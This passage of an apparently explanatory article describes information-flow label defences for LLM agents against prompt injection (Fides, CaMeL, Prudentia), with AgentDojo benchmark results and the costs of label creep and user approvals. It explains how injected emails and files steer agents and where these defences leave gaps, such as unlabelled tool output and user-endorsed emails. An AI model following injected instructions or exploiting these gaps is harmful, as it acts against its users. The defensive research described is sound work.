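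An attacker who wrote one of the emails can cause a false calendar entry, but cannot make the planning model use a different tool. CaMeL divides the work between two models in a similar way. Fides adds an answer's type to its label, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no but reject untrusted free text.

Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful AgentDojo attacks against an ordinary GPT-4o agent, after removing cases that the benchmark had scored wrongly, and none against an agent using Fides with its policies. The policies alone also stopped every attack on the ordinary agent, so the variables in Fides mainly helped the agent get more work done. The researchers left the restricted answers out of these tests because few tasks needed them.

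| Tasks completed without an attack | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with policies | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| Fides with policies | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Task completion fell sharply in banking because many of those tasks ask the agent to read a file and do what it says. Injection attacks rely on the same behavior, so the policies cannot allow it without someone's approval. Some of the other losses came from GPT-4o's difficulty with variables. Fides completed 68% of travel tasks with o1, a stronger model at the time, compared with 41% with GPT-4o.

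Labeling the confidential report as readable only by the project's maintainers could prevent the leak in DelegateGuard's code-review workflow. Fides would then block anything derived from the report from being posted on a public page, including the legitimate comment. Someone would have to declassify the comment, which means deciding that it is safe to publish. Roy's compiler has the same problem, because its error messages would inherit the labels of the protected files.

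Fides tracks data that moves from one place to another, but it does not stop leaks through behaviour, where an observer infers private information from the agent's choice of tool or the time it takes. Costa and colleagues considered a stronger guarantee too restrictive, because the agent could take almost no visible action after reading something private. Liang and colleagues tested Fides and three other defences against their web-link attack, and none lowered the attacker's score by more than 0.03.

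Microsoft added Fides to its Agent Framework in 2026 as an experimental feature. According to Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), the framework treats a tool's output as trusted and public if the developer forgets to label it. This is the opposite of the fail-safe defaults that Saltzer and Schroeder recommended. Microsoft has asked developers whether the default should change.

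### The cost of spreading labels

Restrictive labels tend to spread until they block harmless work, a problem called label creep. Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated it in groups of 5 to 20 agents. An agent that handled or passed on sensitive data kept the sensitive label for the rest of the task. The researchers measured

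loss = (tool calls made under a sensitive label) / (all tool calls)

Some loss is unavoidable, because some calls need sensitive data. When every message went through a central orchestrator, the loss was about 5 percentage points higher than when agents that needed each other's results could communicate directly, because the orchestrator picked up every label and passed it on. Connecting all the agents directly avoids this, but n agents then have n(n − 1)/2 links to monitor, or 10 for 5 agents and 190 for 20. Giving all the sensitive tools to a few agents also reduced the loss.

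No arrangement eliminated the loss, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that agents also need safe ways to remove labels. The simulation used no language models, and it assumed that agents never forget and that nobody removes a label. Real systems could relax both assumptions, which could reduce the loss. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) adds that tracking labels can slow agents down considerably, since some methods run extra model calls to work out which data influenced a result.

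The Fides team argues that comparing the number of completed tasks makes labels look worse than they are, because many agents already ask a person to approve every action with serious consequences. So in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) counted approvals on AgentDojo, using the model o3-mini. Their agent, Prudentia, builds on Fides but also tells the planning model about the labels and policies, so the model can avoid plans that would need approval.

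| Agent | Tasks completed without any approval |
|---|---|
| Asks about every consequential action | 24.3% |
| Asks only when labels break a policy | 35.5% |
| Fides | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | 59.1% |

The first agent needed about 48 approvals for the tasks it completed, and Fides needed about 19. This means less work for users who would otherwise review every action. Users who let their agents run without asking don't get that benefit, but they still have tasks blocked.

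Prudentia also reduces approvals by letting the user endorse untrusted data. If an email lists ten jobs, the user can approve the email once instead of approving ten actions, and the agent then treats the email as trusted. Kolluri and colleagues assumed in their tests that people would stop any action caused by an injection. But Anthropic's testers missed most of the dangerous commands, and a hidden instruction in a long email is probably harder to spot. A user who misses it and endorses the email lets the agent follow that instruction, up to the limits of the agent's grant.
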